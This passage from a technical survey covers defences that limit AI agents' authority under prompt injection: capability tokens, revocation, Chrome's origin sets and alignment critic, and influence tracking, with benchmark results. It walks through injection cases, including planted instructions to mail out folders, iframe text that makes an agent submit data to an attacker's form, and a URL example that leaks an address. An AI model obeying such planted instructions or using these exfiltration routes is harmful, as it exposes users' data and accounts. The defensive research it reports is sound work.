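HMAC combines a key and a text into a code from which nobody can recover the key. An agent with sig₂ can add another restriction, but it can't recover sig₁ to drop "read only". The issuer knows the secret, so it can recompute the chain and check it. Veski and colleagues found that narrowing a token this way was 30 times faster than OAuth Token Exchange, an existing standard in which a central server has to issue each narrower token. *Attenuating Authorization Tokens for Agentic Delegation Chains* (Niyikiza, 2026) and *Verifiable Attenuated Delegation for AI Agent Chains* (Asor, 2026) are draft proposals for internet standards for tokens that services can verify offline.

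### What DelegateGuard adds

An AgentCap token covers one action on one resource. Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, instead describe an agent's whole authority for a task in a single grant:

G = ⟨h, p, L, O, S, d, r⟩.

Here *h* is the holder, *p* the purpose, *L* the labels of the data it may move, *O* the permitted operations, *S* the permitted sinks, *d* the remaining delegation depth and *r* a flag showing whether the grant has been revoked. A monitor outside the model allows an action only if the actor is the holder, the purpose falls within *p*, and the operation, labels and sink are in the permitted sets. Every grant in the chain back to the user must also be active.

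A sub-agent's grant can't contain anything that its parent's grant lacks, and its depth must be lower than the parent's. Purposes work like folder paths, so `contract.summarize/format` falls within `contract.summarize`. Revoking a grant also revokes every grant below it. Otherwise, a worker waiting in a queue when the user cancels the task would still have its authority when it ran.

### A sub-agent that asks for more

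Suppose a user gives an agent access to two folders and lets it send mail to one domain, `partner.example`. The agent starts a sub-agent to summarise folder A. Under DelegateGuard, their grants could look like this:

| | Main agent | Sub-agent |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | report | report/summarise |
| Data labels | folder A, folder B | folder A |
| Operations | read, transform, transmit, delegate | read, transform, transmit, delegate |
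| Sinks | internal messages, mail to `partner.example` | internal messages |
| Delegation depth | 2 | 1 |

A file in folder A contains a planted instruction to mail out both folders, and the sub-agent follows it.

- It tries to read folder B. The monitor refuses because its grant covers only folder A.
- It tries to send mail. The monitor refuses because mail isn't among its sinks.
- It tries to start a helper that can send mail. The monitor refuses to create the grant, because the sub-agent can't pass on a sink it doesn't have.
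- It tries to use the main agent's grant. The monitor refuses because the sub-agent isn't the holder.

Under AgentCap, the main agent would hold separate tokens for folder A, folder B and mail, and would pass only the folder A token to the sub-agent. The gateway would then refuse the sub-agent's calls to folder B or mail because it has no token for them. The sub-agent might still ask the policy engine for a mail token, and none of the seven conditions the paper lists depends on what the main agent passed on, so the deployer's policy would have to forbid this.

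Each refusal by DelegateGuard's monitor depends only on the grant in question and the chain above it, not on how many agents are running or which of them can exchange messages. A reviewer of the ServiceNow platform, by contrast, had to consider every pair of agents that might find each other. Each hop can only keep or reduce the authority it receives, so an agent ten hops away can't have more than the user gave. A new mail service connected during the run isn't in anyone's grant, so the monitor blocks its use until the user or an administrator adds it.

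### What the experiments tested

Tran-Truong and colleagues built five office workflows, such as summarising a confidential contract and reviewing code. They created 45 attacks by planting instructions in tool results, shared memory and messages between agents. Each attack aimed to make an agent send data to an outside address, give a helper extra authority, or act after the user had cancelled the task. Two small open models, Qwen2.5-7B and Llama-3.2-3B, attempted the harmful action in 42 and 44 of the attacks respectively, and DelegateGuard blocked every attempt. Any correct implementation would have blocked them, because each action used authority that the grant didn't include or that the user had revoked.

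In a more realistic test, agents held conversations and could try again after a refusal. Data leaked in 38 of 45 attacked runs without the monitor and in 9 with it. All 45 runs without an attack completed their task. DelegateGuard also refused ten further attacks that a fixed list of permitted sinks allowed. In these attacks, a worker either acted after cancellation or sent the wrong data to a permitted sink.

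These results depend on the user's original grant, which trusted software called an adapter creates from a template. When the researchers added one unnecessary outside address to the grant, 30 of the 45 attacks succeeded.

Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on 2,003 attacked cases from AgentDojo and InjecAgent, another benchmark of injection attacks. They wrote the policies before the tests and didn't change them afterwards. "Tasks completed" below means the user's own tasks that the agent completed while under attack.

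| Benchmark and model | Attack success, without and with AgentCap | Tasks completed, without and with AgentCap |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0.0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 62.2% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0.0% | 73.0% → 65.4% |

These figures provide little evidence about delegation, because AgentDojo's tasks involve a single agent. Some of the protection probably comes from a different part of AgentCap, which works a little like CaMeL's provenance tags and rejects a sensitive argument, such as a payee, if the value appears only in untrusted content. Some of the remaining attacks succeeded because the policy didn't protect the argument or didn't label the field it came from. The evidence on delegation comes from scripted scenarios, in which AgentCap refused all nine attempts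 to expand delegated authority or reuse it in another session.

Dantuluri and Sundi built a broker that issues a narrower token at each hop and ties it to the receiving agent's identity. They tested it in only four scenarios: a confused deputy, a stolen token, an agent seeking extra permissions and a compromised sub-agent. The broker blocked all four attacks, which had all succeeded against a default system that the researchers wrote to represent common practice. It also withstood 11 attacks on its own design and rejected 200,000 forged tokens. A stolen token still worked if the attacker could also present the victim's identity.

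In 2,000 simulated delegations, a compromised sub-agent had access to an average of 1.5 actions with the broker, compared with all 8,100 when agents shared one credential. The 1.5 is just the average task size in the simulation. None of these tests used a language model. Both researchers work for VotalAI, which sells a product based on the same principles.

### Taking authority back

Revocation is harder when two agents share a sub-agent. Suppose agents A and B both delegate to C, which delegates to D. If A withdraws its delegation, a system that cuts off C and everything below it also stops work that B still authorises. Liu, Yu and Jiang (2026), in *VERA*, propose cutting off only the agents in

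reach(G) \ reach(G \ {e}),

where *G* is the graph of delegations, *e* is the withdrawn one, and reach gives all agents that still have a path from a trusted starting point. In this example the set is empty, because C and D still have a path through B. In 500 replayed LangGraph runs, the rule preserved all 320 cases in which a shared agent would have wrongly lost its authority.

This calculation needs a map of the delegations. DelegateGuard avoids the calculation by giving each capability at most one parent. C would hold one capability from A and another from B, and revoking the one from A would leave the one from B in place. But if C had derived D's capability from the one A granted, D would have to stop until C issued it a new one.

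Services also have to find out when a token has been revoked. *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* (2026) describes using either tokens that expire after about five minutes or a check of the whole chain on each use, which takes longer as the chain grows. An expiry time limits how long an agent can use a revoked token, but *The Bureaucracy of Speed* (2026) points out that a fast agent can do more damage in that time. At 50 calls a second, a token with 60 seconds left allows 3,000 more calls. A limit of ten calls stays the same however fast the agent is. AgentCap's tokens limit both the time and the number of calls.

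Immediate revocation may not stop work that a service has already accepted. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents*, give the example of a job that enters a queue before the user cancels. A remote worker can still carry it out after the original program has exited and its token is invalid. They propose a fence, which checks each job at the point where it would take effect and refuses any that relies on the old authority. In a small test, a scheduled job still took effect after cancellation alone, but not when the service had a fence.

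Cancellation is unreliable in existing software too. Khan (*Stop Means Stop*, 2026) tested six agent frameworks and found that in all six, tools run in certain ways could still take effect after the run was cancelled. Under MCP, the receiver of a cancellation "is not obligated to actually stop the work" (*Airlock*, 2026).

### Leaks through a permitted sink

All nine leaks in DelegateGuard's conversation test came from the code-review workflow, where a worker reads about an unpublished vulnerability and has to post a review comment that outsiders can see. A planted instruction can make the worker include the secret details in that comment.

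Tran-Truong and colleagues' Proposition 1 shows that this can happen with any monitor that decides from the holder, purpose, labels, operation, sink and chain of grants, but ignores a message's content and length. It is therefore not a fault in their software. Suppose such a monitor lets an agent send a harmless comment to a sink that outsiders can observe. It must also allow a comment that contains a secret if nothing it checks differs between the two.

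The proof assumes that both messages have the same labels. In the researchers' tests of more inventive attacks, the agent declared the labels itself, so it could send secret data without declaring any labels. Software that tracked labels, as FIDES does, would prevent this. But it wouldn't help with the code review, because a useful comment has to draw on the same confidential material as a comment that leaks it. Both comments would have the same label, so a label check couldn't refuse only the leak.

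The proposition need not apply to a monitor that examines content. In the same tests, a filter that blocked any message containing the secret prevented leaks in all 26 attacks, while DelegateGuard allowed three leaks. However, the filter also blocked four of the five legitimate tasks, and DelegateGuard blocked none. Another option is to limit how much information the worker can send. If the worker could only choose between "approve" and "request changes", each review would reveal at most one bit. That might be enough for some reviews, but not for one that has to explain a bug.

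### Who may act and what may flow

Denning held that access controls are not enough, and *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) gives a reason. To keep a file secret with permissions alone, its owner would have to give access only to programs that won't leak it, and permissions can't identify those programs.

In the two-folder example, the sub-agent may read folder A and reply to the main agent, which may send mail to `partner.example`. Together, these permissions let the contents of folder A reach the partner, even if the user meant to share only folder B. Influence can travel the same way. The sub-agent can't send mail, but its reply can include the planted instruction, which the main agent has the authority to follow. A label check could stop both flows by marking folder A as secret and the sub-agent's reply as untrusted.

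Labels can't replace capabilities either. A sub-agent that has read only trusted, public data would pass every label check, but it shouldn't necessarily be able to delete the user's folders.

AgentCap partly controls flows by forbidding some combinations of tokens. A policy can stop an agent from holding tokens to read private files and to send mail at the same time. But the tokens may last only seconds, and whatever the agent has read stays in the model's context. If the rule counts only tokens that are still valid, an agent could read a private file, wait for that token to expire and then get a token to send mail. A context label would still include S, so a label check would block the message.

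## Chrome's origin sets: adding websites to an agent's reach during a task

DelegateGuard's grants can only stay the same or shrink as agents pass them on. But an agent that browses the web often has to extend its reach during a task, because it may discover partway through that it needs another website. Google added such an agent, called auto browse, to its Chrome browser in January 2026. Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026) lists shopping and comparing hotel prices among the agent's uses. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) described Google's security design in December 2025.

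### Origins and the same-origin policy

A web origin is the combination of a page's scheme (such as http or https), host name and port number. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of two pages at `http://www.example.com`, which share an origin. Switching to https, dropping the "www" or adding port 8080 changes the origin.

The same-origin policy, which dates from 1995 according to the University of Washington, stops a script on one origin from reading pages on another. It lets people keep their bank's website open in one tab and an untrustworthy site in another. It also applies to iframes, which display one web page inside another and often hold advertisements.

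The same-origin policy restricts scripts but not people, who can copy an account number from one site and paste it into another. A browsing agent can do the same without the user noticing. It reads the first page, keeps the text in its context and types it into the second. No script has crossed between origins, so the browser's usual checks don't apply. In a communication graph, the agent can add an arrow between any two sites it visits. For this reason, Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending the same-origin policy to agents.

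### Two sets and a gate

Google's version of this idea is called Agent Origin Sets. For each session, the design keeps two lists:

- **Read-only origins.** The agent may read content from these sites.
- **Read-writable origins.** The agent may also click and type on these sites.

If an iframe's origin is on neither list, Chrome leaves its content out of what the model receives. Anything the agent has read may go only to read-writable origins.

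The planner, a Gemini model that reads web pages and chooses the next action, can propose new origins. A gating function decides whether they are relevant to the user's task. The function receives no untrusted web content, so an attacker can't give it instructions by planting text on a page. The planner can also use pages the user has shared in the session, but it still needs the function's approval to add an origin.

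A page can also send the tab to another site without a request from the planner. In either case, a model checks whether the new origin is relevant before the agent can continue there.

URLs need a separate check because just opening a page can send data out. Planted instructions might lead the planner to open `https://deals.example/?address=12+Elm+Street`, and the site's owner could then read the street address in the server's log. Chrome therefore restricts URLs written by the model to known, public ones, using a fixed rule rather than a model's judgement.

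### What the browser enforces and what a model decides

A second Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, checks every action the planner proposes. It receives metadata about the action but no unfiltered web content, and vetoes any action that doesn't serve the user's goal. After a veto, the planner gets feedback and tries again, or returns control to the user if it fails repeatedly. A variant of the Critic checks new origins.

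Parker names the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL as partial inspirations. Unlike CaMeL's planner, Chrome's reads untrusted pages, so text planted in a page can change the plan, and the later checks have to catch the result.

| Decision | What makes it |
|---|---|
| May the agent act on this origin? | The browser, using the session's list |
| Should this origin join the list? | A model that gets no web content |
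| May the agent open a URL that the model wrote? | A fixed rule |
| Does this action serve the user's goal? | The User Alignment Critic |
| Does this page contain a prompt injection? | A classifier that reads the page |
| May the agent open a banking or medical site? | The user, prompted by a fixed list of sensitive sites |
| May the agent sign in with a saved password? | The user |
| May the agent pay or send a message? | The user, if the software recognises the action as sensitive |

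The browser can enforce the list even if an attacker has taken over the planner. But the list's contents depend on a model's judgement of relevance, which no theorem covers. Judging relevance is still a narrower problem than predicting what a new site's code will ever do, which is undecidable by the result for new tools.

Attackers can still have some influence on this model even though it doesn't see web content. They choose the domain names of their own sites, and their text can affect which sites the planner proposes once the planner has read it.

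### A shopping task

Parker gives the example of an agent that collects ingredients on one site and fills a shopping cart on another. The session could start with the recipe site, say `recipes.example`, in the read-only set and the grocer, say `grocer.example`, in the read-writable set.

1. The agent reads the recipe. The page also has an advertisement in an iframe from another origin, which Chrome leaves out.
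2. The agent adds the ingredients to the grocer's cart. The Critic approves because this is what the user asked for.
3. A customer review on the grocer's site mentions a coupon at `deals.example`, and the planner proposes to go there. The gate has to judge the site without reading the review. If it refuses, the agent continues without the coupon. If it approves, Chrome adds the site to the read-only set.
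4. The coupon site asks for an email address. The agent can't type one unless the site joins the read-writable set.
5. At the checkout, the agent should stop and ask the user to approve or complete the payment.

Each new site adds more possible data flows than the one the task needs. With *r* read-only and *w* read-writable origins, the sets allow data to flow from one origin to another in *w*(*r* + *w* − 1) ways.

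| Coupon site's status | Flows the sets allow |
|---|---|
| Not admitted | 1: recipe site to grocer |
| Read-only | 2: recipe site to grocer, coupon site to grocer |
| Read-writable | 4: the same two, plus recipe site to coupon site and grocer to coupon site |

The last of these flows could carry the user's home address and past orders from the grocer to the coupon site. The sets allow it, so the Critic would have to catch it. Although the agent read the address before the coupon site was available, the address is still in its context. Parker gives relevance to the task as the test for admitting a site and doesn't mention what the agent has already read. A context label would reflect what the agent has read, since it would include S once the agent had read the grocer's account page.

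The sets also can't limit what the agent chooses within a permitted site. At a workshop session recorded in W3C's *Agentic Browsing and the Web's Security Model* (2025), one participant objected that a shop could plant text that steers an agent to a slightly overpriced product. Another replied that limiting the agent to certain sites would still remove much of the danger, and that overpaying for a sweater was less frightening than a shop reading the user's email.

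### The Washington study

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers with built-in agents in late January and early February 2026. They built web pages on two domains, each with different facts about an invented person, Alice. One page stated that she liked cats, and an iframe from the other domain stated that she liked horses. They then asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the answer included horses, the agent had read across origins. They counted a behaviour as present if they saw it once, and tried at least three times in fresh chats before counting it as absent.

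They also tested whether each agent would type into a form, first when the user asked it to, and then when the instruction to type was written in the page and the user told the agent to do whatever the page said.

| Browser | Read iframes from another origin | Typed at the user's request | Typed on the page's instructions |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | Yes, with auto browse | No |
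| Claude for Chrome | Yes | Yes | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | Yes, except passwords | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas, ordinary mode | No | With permission | With permission |
| Brave, Edge and Firefox | No | No | No |

An agent that can read across origins and type into pages can be used to steal data if a prompt injection succeeds. Roesner and Kohlbrenner demonstrated this in Atlas's Agent Mode. Their test page contained an iframe from another origin and a form that submitted itself. When the user asked for a summary, the agent followed instructions on the page to include the iframe's contents and type the summary into the form, which sent it to the attacker's server.

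The attack also worked in reverse, with the embedded page stealing from the page around it. This is more worrying because a malicious advertisement could use it against an email site. The first version is harder to use against real targets because most sensitive sites restrict other sites from embedding them or withhold the user's login when embedded.

The researchers found the preconditions for this theft in Chrome, Claude for Chrome and Comet, but no working injection for any of them. They made only simple attempts, because finding sophisticated injections was not their aim, and in all three products the model refused to follow the page's instructions. OpenAI declined their report on Atlas because the report did not include a complete prompt injection attack.

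Data can also move between sites through chat history. Atlas, Chrome and Comet all used information from earlier chats in later ones. A false phone number from a fake bank page could come up weeks later, when the user asks for the bank's number. Chrome's origin sets apply to one session, so a site can influence a later session without being in that session's sets.

### Which parts Google had built

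Parker wrote in December 2025 that the first version tracked only the read-writable set. Tracking only that set would limit where the agent could act, but would not by itself hide irrelevant iframes. The Washington results fit this account, since Chrome read iframes from another origin a few weeks later.

The read-only set is the part of the design best suited to stop the theft shown in Atlas. If the user asked about an email page, Chrome would withhold the advertisement's iframe, so the model would never receive the planted instruction. Even if the model had received it, the read-writable set might have blocked the last step by preventing the agent from typing into the advertisement. Roesner and Kohlbrenner didn't test this, and wrote that it was unclear how Chrome judges relevance or how well that judgement withstands malicious input.

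The public source code of Chromium (2025), the project on which Chrome is built, shows that the browser keeps a list of origins that the agent may visit without further confirmation. Google's server, a model or the user can add to it during a task. Sensitive sites have a separate list, so approval of an ordinary site never covers them. The gate checks the main page in a tab but not the iframes inside it.

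In one version of Chromium's code, the gate and the prompt for sensitive sites are on by default, but the extra confirmation for new origins is off. A tool request can also add an origin implicitly by default. These defaults don't show how auto browse worked for users, because Google can change them remotely and run other checks on its servers.

Google has since extended the feature to more users. *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* (Kanchwala, 2026) reported in October that it had arrived in India on desktop and Android. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026), an August account of Chrome's security for businesses, again describes limiting the agent to origins relevant to the task but doesn't mention a read-only set, so it is unclear whether Google has built one. The account also describes controls that let companies apply an employee's access restrictions and their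 own rules on sensitive data to the agent.

A newly admitted site may also offer tools to the browser's agent through WebMCP, a proposed standard. *WebMCP Can Be Used To Hijack AI Agents, Chrome Warns* (Montti, 2026) reports Google's warning that attackers can manipulate agents through such tools.

### Leaks and approvals on permitted sites

Wang and colleagues measured leaks between two sites the user had chosen. In their benchmark, the agent first handles private information on one site, such as an airline or a pharmacy. The user then gives it a harmless task on a second site, such as posting a comment, where an attacker has planted instructions to reveal the information. Atlas leaked it in 99 of 150 runs. The study didn't include Chrome. Chrome's Critic might have vetoed some of these comments, but its origin sets would probably have allowed them because the task required reading the first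 site and writing to the second.

Without planted instructions, the agents leaked nothing between separately visited pages. But when the private page was in an iframe and the user asked the agent to write a summary of the whole page in a text box, the one browser tested this way leaked private data every time, even though no attacker was involved.

The researchers' remedy, SOPGuard, labels data with its origin and carries the label over to text the model generates from that data. It requires the user's approval before the agent writes the text to a different origin. SOPGuard stopped every leak in the benchmark and added 2 to 6 percent to the running time. Unlike the origin sets, it requests approval for a particular flow from one site to another. In the shopping task, however, every ingredient the agent types into the grocer's search box comes from the recipe site, so the user might have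 to approve many harmless flows.

Some attacks don't need to move private data. In one scenario from *The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026), a user asks an agent to summarise a page about a billing export. A note planted on the page claims that an access review is holding up the work. The agent follows a link to a second site and approves a stranger's access to the user's account. In another scenario, the user asks the agent to complete the setup tasks in a guide, and the attacker has added a task that sends the account's billing events to an outside address.

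The unauthorised action went through in all 73 attacked runs, which used Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5 in an open-source browser agent. When Hossen told Haiku that only the user's task could authorise such an approval, 7 of 10 attacks still succeeded. Chrome's Critic might catch an approval during a task that asked only for a summary. An approval during the setup task would be harder to catch, because the attacker's addition looks like the work the user requested.

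In Hossen's own defence, the service that receives the agent's request checks it against a list of the exact approvals or addresses that the user's task authorises. The service gets this list before the agent starts, and the list must come from a source that the agent can't alter. The agent still sent the harmful request in all 70 attacked runs, but the service rejected every one. It accepted the action in all 73 runs where the user had asked for it. A user who asks only for "any pending setup tasks" has authorised no address, so the user would have to explicitly approve even a legitimate one.

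## NeuroTaint and SafeFlow: tracking influence when wording changes

Hossen's check compares an exact address with an approved list, but secrets and instructions rarely keep their exact form once a language model has processed them. In one test case, a research agent reads a web page containing an instruction to work a confidential patient note into its memo in "polished analyst language". The memo then gives the patient's diagnosis and treatment in new words, so a search for copied phrases would miss the leak.

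Labelling the whole context catches the leak however it is worded, but causes label creep. In *GIF*, Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026) point out that any word a model reads may affect any word it writes later, so careful tracking must include every input. Several newer systems instead estimate which inputs influenced an action. They can allow more harmless work, but their estimates can be wrong.

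### Reconstructing a flow from the log

Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe NeuroTaint, which audits an agent's log after the run. The deployer lists the tools that count as sources and sinks. For each call to a sink, NeuroTaint then works through three stages:

1. **Find the possible sources.** NeuroTaint keeps a graph with a point for every tool call. When the agent saves something to memory, NeuroTaint saves its labels too, and restores them when the agent retrieves it. In the paper's example, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast in one session and uses it in a report days later. The graph connects the report to the original forecast.
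2. **Look for the source's content in the call.** The first test looks for a random code that NeuroTaint attached to the source's text during the run. The second measures shared wording. The third converts both texts into embeddings, lists of numbers that represent meaning, and measures how similar they are. One planted sentence hardly changes the embedding of a long page, so the last test splits the page into chunks and compares each one with the call.
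3. **Ask what would have happened without the source.** NeuroTaint does this only if the second stage finds nothing.

The third stage detects influence when none of the source's text appears in the tool call. For example, a planted email might claim that company policy now requires the agent to delete old invoices. The agent then calls a deletion tool with invoice numbers from the company's own database, so the call contains nothing from the email. NeuroTaint replaces the email with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call. If the answer is no, NeuroTaint reports that the email influenced the deletion.

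A second model predicts the answer, since NeuroTaint doesn't run the agent again. The test also removes one source at a time. If two planted emails gave the same instruction, the agent might delete the invoices after reading either one. The model could then correctly predict that removing each email alone wouldn't prevent the deletion, and the test would find neither email responsible.

### What TaintBench measures

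Cai and colleagues knew of no benchmark that labelled flows from sources to sinks, so they built TaintBench. It has 400 scenarios, 20 for each of 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, the source is meant to reach or influence the sink. They compared NeuroTaint with a baseline modelled on FIDES, which mainly looks for a path from a source tool to a sink tool.

| | NeuroTaint | FIDES-style baseline |
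|---|---|---|
| Flows found, out of 200 | 187 | 108 |
| False alarms, out of 200 | 16 | 106 |
| Precision (share of alarms that were correct) | 0.921 | 0.505 |
| Recall (share of flows found) | 0.935 | 0.540 |
| F1 (precision and recall combined) | 0.928 | 0.522 |

The baseline's F1 was below the 0.667 that a detector would get by raising an alarm in all 400 scenarios. The baseline raised no alarms in four of the frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses. It also missed 23 of the 40 cases of influence without copied content. FIDES should catch such cases, because it gives every proposed call the label of the whole context, so the comparison is weak evidence of how well FIDES works as a defence. On two established benchmarks that label unsafe actions instead of flows, NeuroTaint and the baseline had almost identical scores.

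NeuroTaint's false alarms show a limit of searching by meaning. In 14 harmless scenarios, the text at the sink was about the same topic as the source but didn't come from it, and NeuroTaint flagged all 14. It flagged only 2 of the other 186 harmless scenarios, which may be partly because it uses a similarity threshold of 0.95 for "safe-control policies" instead of the usual 0.60. If those policies belong to the benchmark's harmless scenarios, users should expect more false alarms in practice, because they can't know in advance which runs are harmless and should get the higher threshold.

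A second check could remove some of the false alarms. When the researchers had Claude Opus 4.6 review the 203 flagged scenarios, it classified 179 of the 187 real flows as unsafe and dismissed all 16 false alarms.

The audit takes about a quarter of a second per run, but it comes too late to stop anything. *LMLineage* (2026) describes a tool that works during the run and traces each sentence of a model's output to passages in its input. Tracing takes seconds and happens while the agent works on its next turn, so an agent that doesn't wait may act before the trace is finished.

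### Holding an action until the path is clear

*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that decides whether to allow an irreversible action before it takes effect. The paper's example is a request to read a configuration file, extract a login token and email it. One agent reads the file, another rewrites the contents and a third prepares the email. Each step might look ordinary to a filter that checks only that step. SafeFlow lets the agents prepare the email but checks the path from the file to the outside address before the email can be sent.

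Language models do some of this work, and fixed rules do the rest:

| Step | What does it |
|---|---|
| Label the risks in the request, such as access to credentials | A language model, with keyword patterns and information about the tools |
| Divide the request into subtasks | A language model |
| Copy labels along messages and handovers | Fixed rules |
| Summarise the evidence at each point in the graph | A language model |
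| Run reversible actions and hold irreversible ones | Fixed rules |
| Release or discard the held actions | Fixed rules |

The rules block any path from a protected source to an outside recipient unless an explicit release condition allows it. They also block untrusted content from reaching the instructions that control the planner. Other held actions go ahead only if the task requires them and their target is authorised. A model can supply evidence for these checks, but it can't remove a label or release an action. It can still cause a failure by omitting a label at the start, because the source is then not treated as protected.

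Dai and colleagues tested SafeFlow on 440 attacks from four existing benchmarks. They compared it with GuardAgent, AegisLLM and AutoDefense, which use language models to screen prompts and proposed actions. These are simple averages over the four benchmarks:

| Defence | Attack success | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 69.3% | 95.0% |
| AutoDefense | 45.7% | 80.5% |
| AegisLLM | 30.0% | 85.9% |
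| GuardAgent | 27.5% | 86.5% |
| SafeFlow | 12.7% | 90.6% |

Part of SafeFlow's advantage comes from using the record of messages between agents, which the other three defences don't use although it was available. When the researchers let only three of SafeFlow's seven labels pass between agents, its attack success rate rose to 22.8 percent.

Attackers can also interfere with the steps that models perform. Planted text that falsely claimed authorisation raised the attack success rate to 15.4 percent, and the most effective of four standard ways of disguising a harmful request raised it to 32.3 percent. CaMeL and FIDES did better than SafeFlow on AgentDojo, but they are designed for trusted users, while SafeFlow also has to handle harmful requests from the user.

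The protection added an average of 3.7 model calls and 8.8 seconds to each harmful workflow.

### New agents and missing links

A graph built from recorded events doesn't require a list of agents in advance. Suppose an agent finds a translation agent halfway through a job and sends it a confidential file. The handover adds a point and an arrow to the graph, and the file's label is carried along the arrow. If the translator then prepares an email to an outsider, the graph contains the whole path from the file to the email. SafeFlow's rules refer to labels and kinds of action, so nobody has to write a new rule for the translator.

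Dai and colleagues' algorithm starts with a given pool of agents and a planner's outline of the work. They tested it on workflows with only 3 to 10 points and didn't test an agent that joins midway.

New tools need more preparation. SafeFlow sends each call through a trusted wrapper, which classifies it as a known kind of action, such as sending data or running code. The wrapper rejects or holds any call it can't classify. NeuroTaint has no such safeguard, so if a new mail tool isn't on the deployer's list of sinks, its calls don't trigger an audit. The deployer could add the tool later and audit the saved log, but the mail would already have gone out.

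Both systems depend on a complete record. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of ways to trace agents' actions, says the record of a tool call should include the tool and its definition, the arguments, the result, and whatever later used that result. The last is the hardest to log because the result may influence a later action only inside the model.

Now suppose the translator gets the file through a shared folder that the software doesn't log. The graph contains a confidential read and a later email, with no path between them. Dai and colleagues list this as a way for attacks to get past SafeFlow. They propose holding any visible high-impact action whose origins are disconnected from the rest of the graph. This is safer, but gaps in the log will also stop legitimate work. If the email itself goes through an unlogged tool, SafeFlow can't hold it, so SafeFlow needs mediation as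 much as any label check does.

### Removing the data along with its label

Influence estimates can also reduce label creep during a run. Suppose an agent reads a trusted handbook and a stranger's web page, then proposes a payment. Ordinary tracking marks the payment {U}, but a system could remove that mark if it estimated that the page had not influenced it.

If the estimate is wrong, the system loses noninterference, because changing an untrusted page can now change a payment labelled as trusted. Later label checks won't catch the mistake, since they rely on the same label.

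Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, avoid this by removing the data as well as the label:

1. The model answers with all the documents in its context.
2. The software leaves out the documents with more restrictive labels and measures how likely the model would be to give the same answer from the rest.
3. If the score falls by no more than a set tolerance, λ, the model answers again from the smaller set.
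4. The software discards the first answer and returns the second, with the less restrictive label.

For example, suppose a user asks for New York's population, and a search returns one trusted page and one untrusted page. The trusted page is enough to answer the question, so the model answers again without the untrusted page, and the new answer counts as trusted.

A planted instruction in the untrusted page can't affect the wording of the second answer, because the model never receives the page in that run. If the software wrongly classifies a document as unimportant, the answer may get worse, but it still depends only on documents its label allows.

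The choice of label is a weaker point because it depends on all the documents. If the software releases an answer only when the secret documents are unnecessary, the release itself could reveal something about them, much as floating labels did in Asbestos. Attackers can also add distracting documents that keep the label restrictive, which Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge could make the system less useful.

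They tested the method on 40 conversations with an agent, 20 of which allowed a less restrictive label. It found that label in 17 of the 20 with a small Llama 2 model and in 19 with a larger one. On a harder set of questions about news articles, it found a less restrictive label in 57 percent of the cases that allowed one with the small model and 39 percent with the larger one. The search needs few extra model calls when there are only two labels, but if each document has its own label, the calls can grow exponentially with the number of documents.

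### Measuring influence in bits

GIF, short for geometric information flow, measures influence inside the model. A language model converts its input into embeddings before processing it. GIF considers small random changes to the embeddings of one passage and estimates how much the next word would reveal about those changes. The score is

GIF = ½ Σ log₂(1 + τλᵢ).

Here τ is the variance of the random changes. Each λᵢ measures how strongly a change in one direction shifts the probabilities of the next word. If τλᵢ is 3 in one direction and 0 in all others, the score is ½ log₂ 4, or 1 bit.

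In the paper's example, an agent screening job applicants reads a CV that contains an instruction to recommend the candidate at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. GIF attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to the planted instruction, 27 to the employer's criteria and 16 to the remaining text. Label tracking would show only that the CV was in the context.

Štorek and colleagues prove that the score is "locally sound". If I is the true amount of information that the next word reveals about the changes, then

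I ≤ GIF + o(τ),

where o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ as the changes become smaller. Lean has checked the proof, which assumes that the model responds smoothly to small changes.

An attacker can replace a whole sentence, not just make small changes. Also, when a planted instruction makes the model almost certain of its next word, small changes hardly affect the probabilities, so the formula's score can be close to zero even if deleting the instruction would change the word. This certainty lowers the scores of all passages together, so their ranking may still be correct, but a fixed limit, such as blocking anything above 10 bits, would be unreliable.

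The software mainly uses the ranking. It gives the most influential passages to a language model, which decides whether to allow the action. The theorem doesn't cover that decision. To save computing time, the software can calculate the scores on a much smaller model than the agent's. This barely changed the results in tests, but the theorem would then apply to the smaller model rather than the agent's.

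To test the ranking without a model's judgement, Štorek and colleagues scored each run by how many of its 50 highest-ranked input tokens (words or parts of words) came from known injections or private data. They then measured how often a run with a violation scored higher than a run without one. Guessing would give 50 percent. Averaged over six models, the result was 91 percent on AgentDojo and 92 percent on another injection benchmark, but only 75 percent on a benchmark of privacy leaks. The ranking is therefore a weaker basis for removing S than for removing U.

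## How the shape of the network affects leaks and blocked work

Estimating influence reduces label creep inside a single model. A designer can also reduce it by choosing which agents communicate, because an agent picks up labels only from what it reads. Two experiments from late 2026 compare communication graphs. One counts the tool calls that restrictive labels would affect, and the other counts how often private data reaches agents that shouldn't have it. Their results favor different graphs.

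### Label creep without a language model

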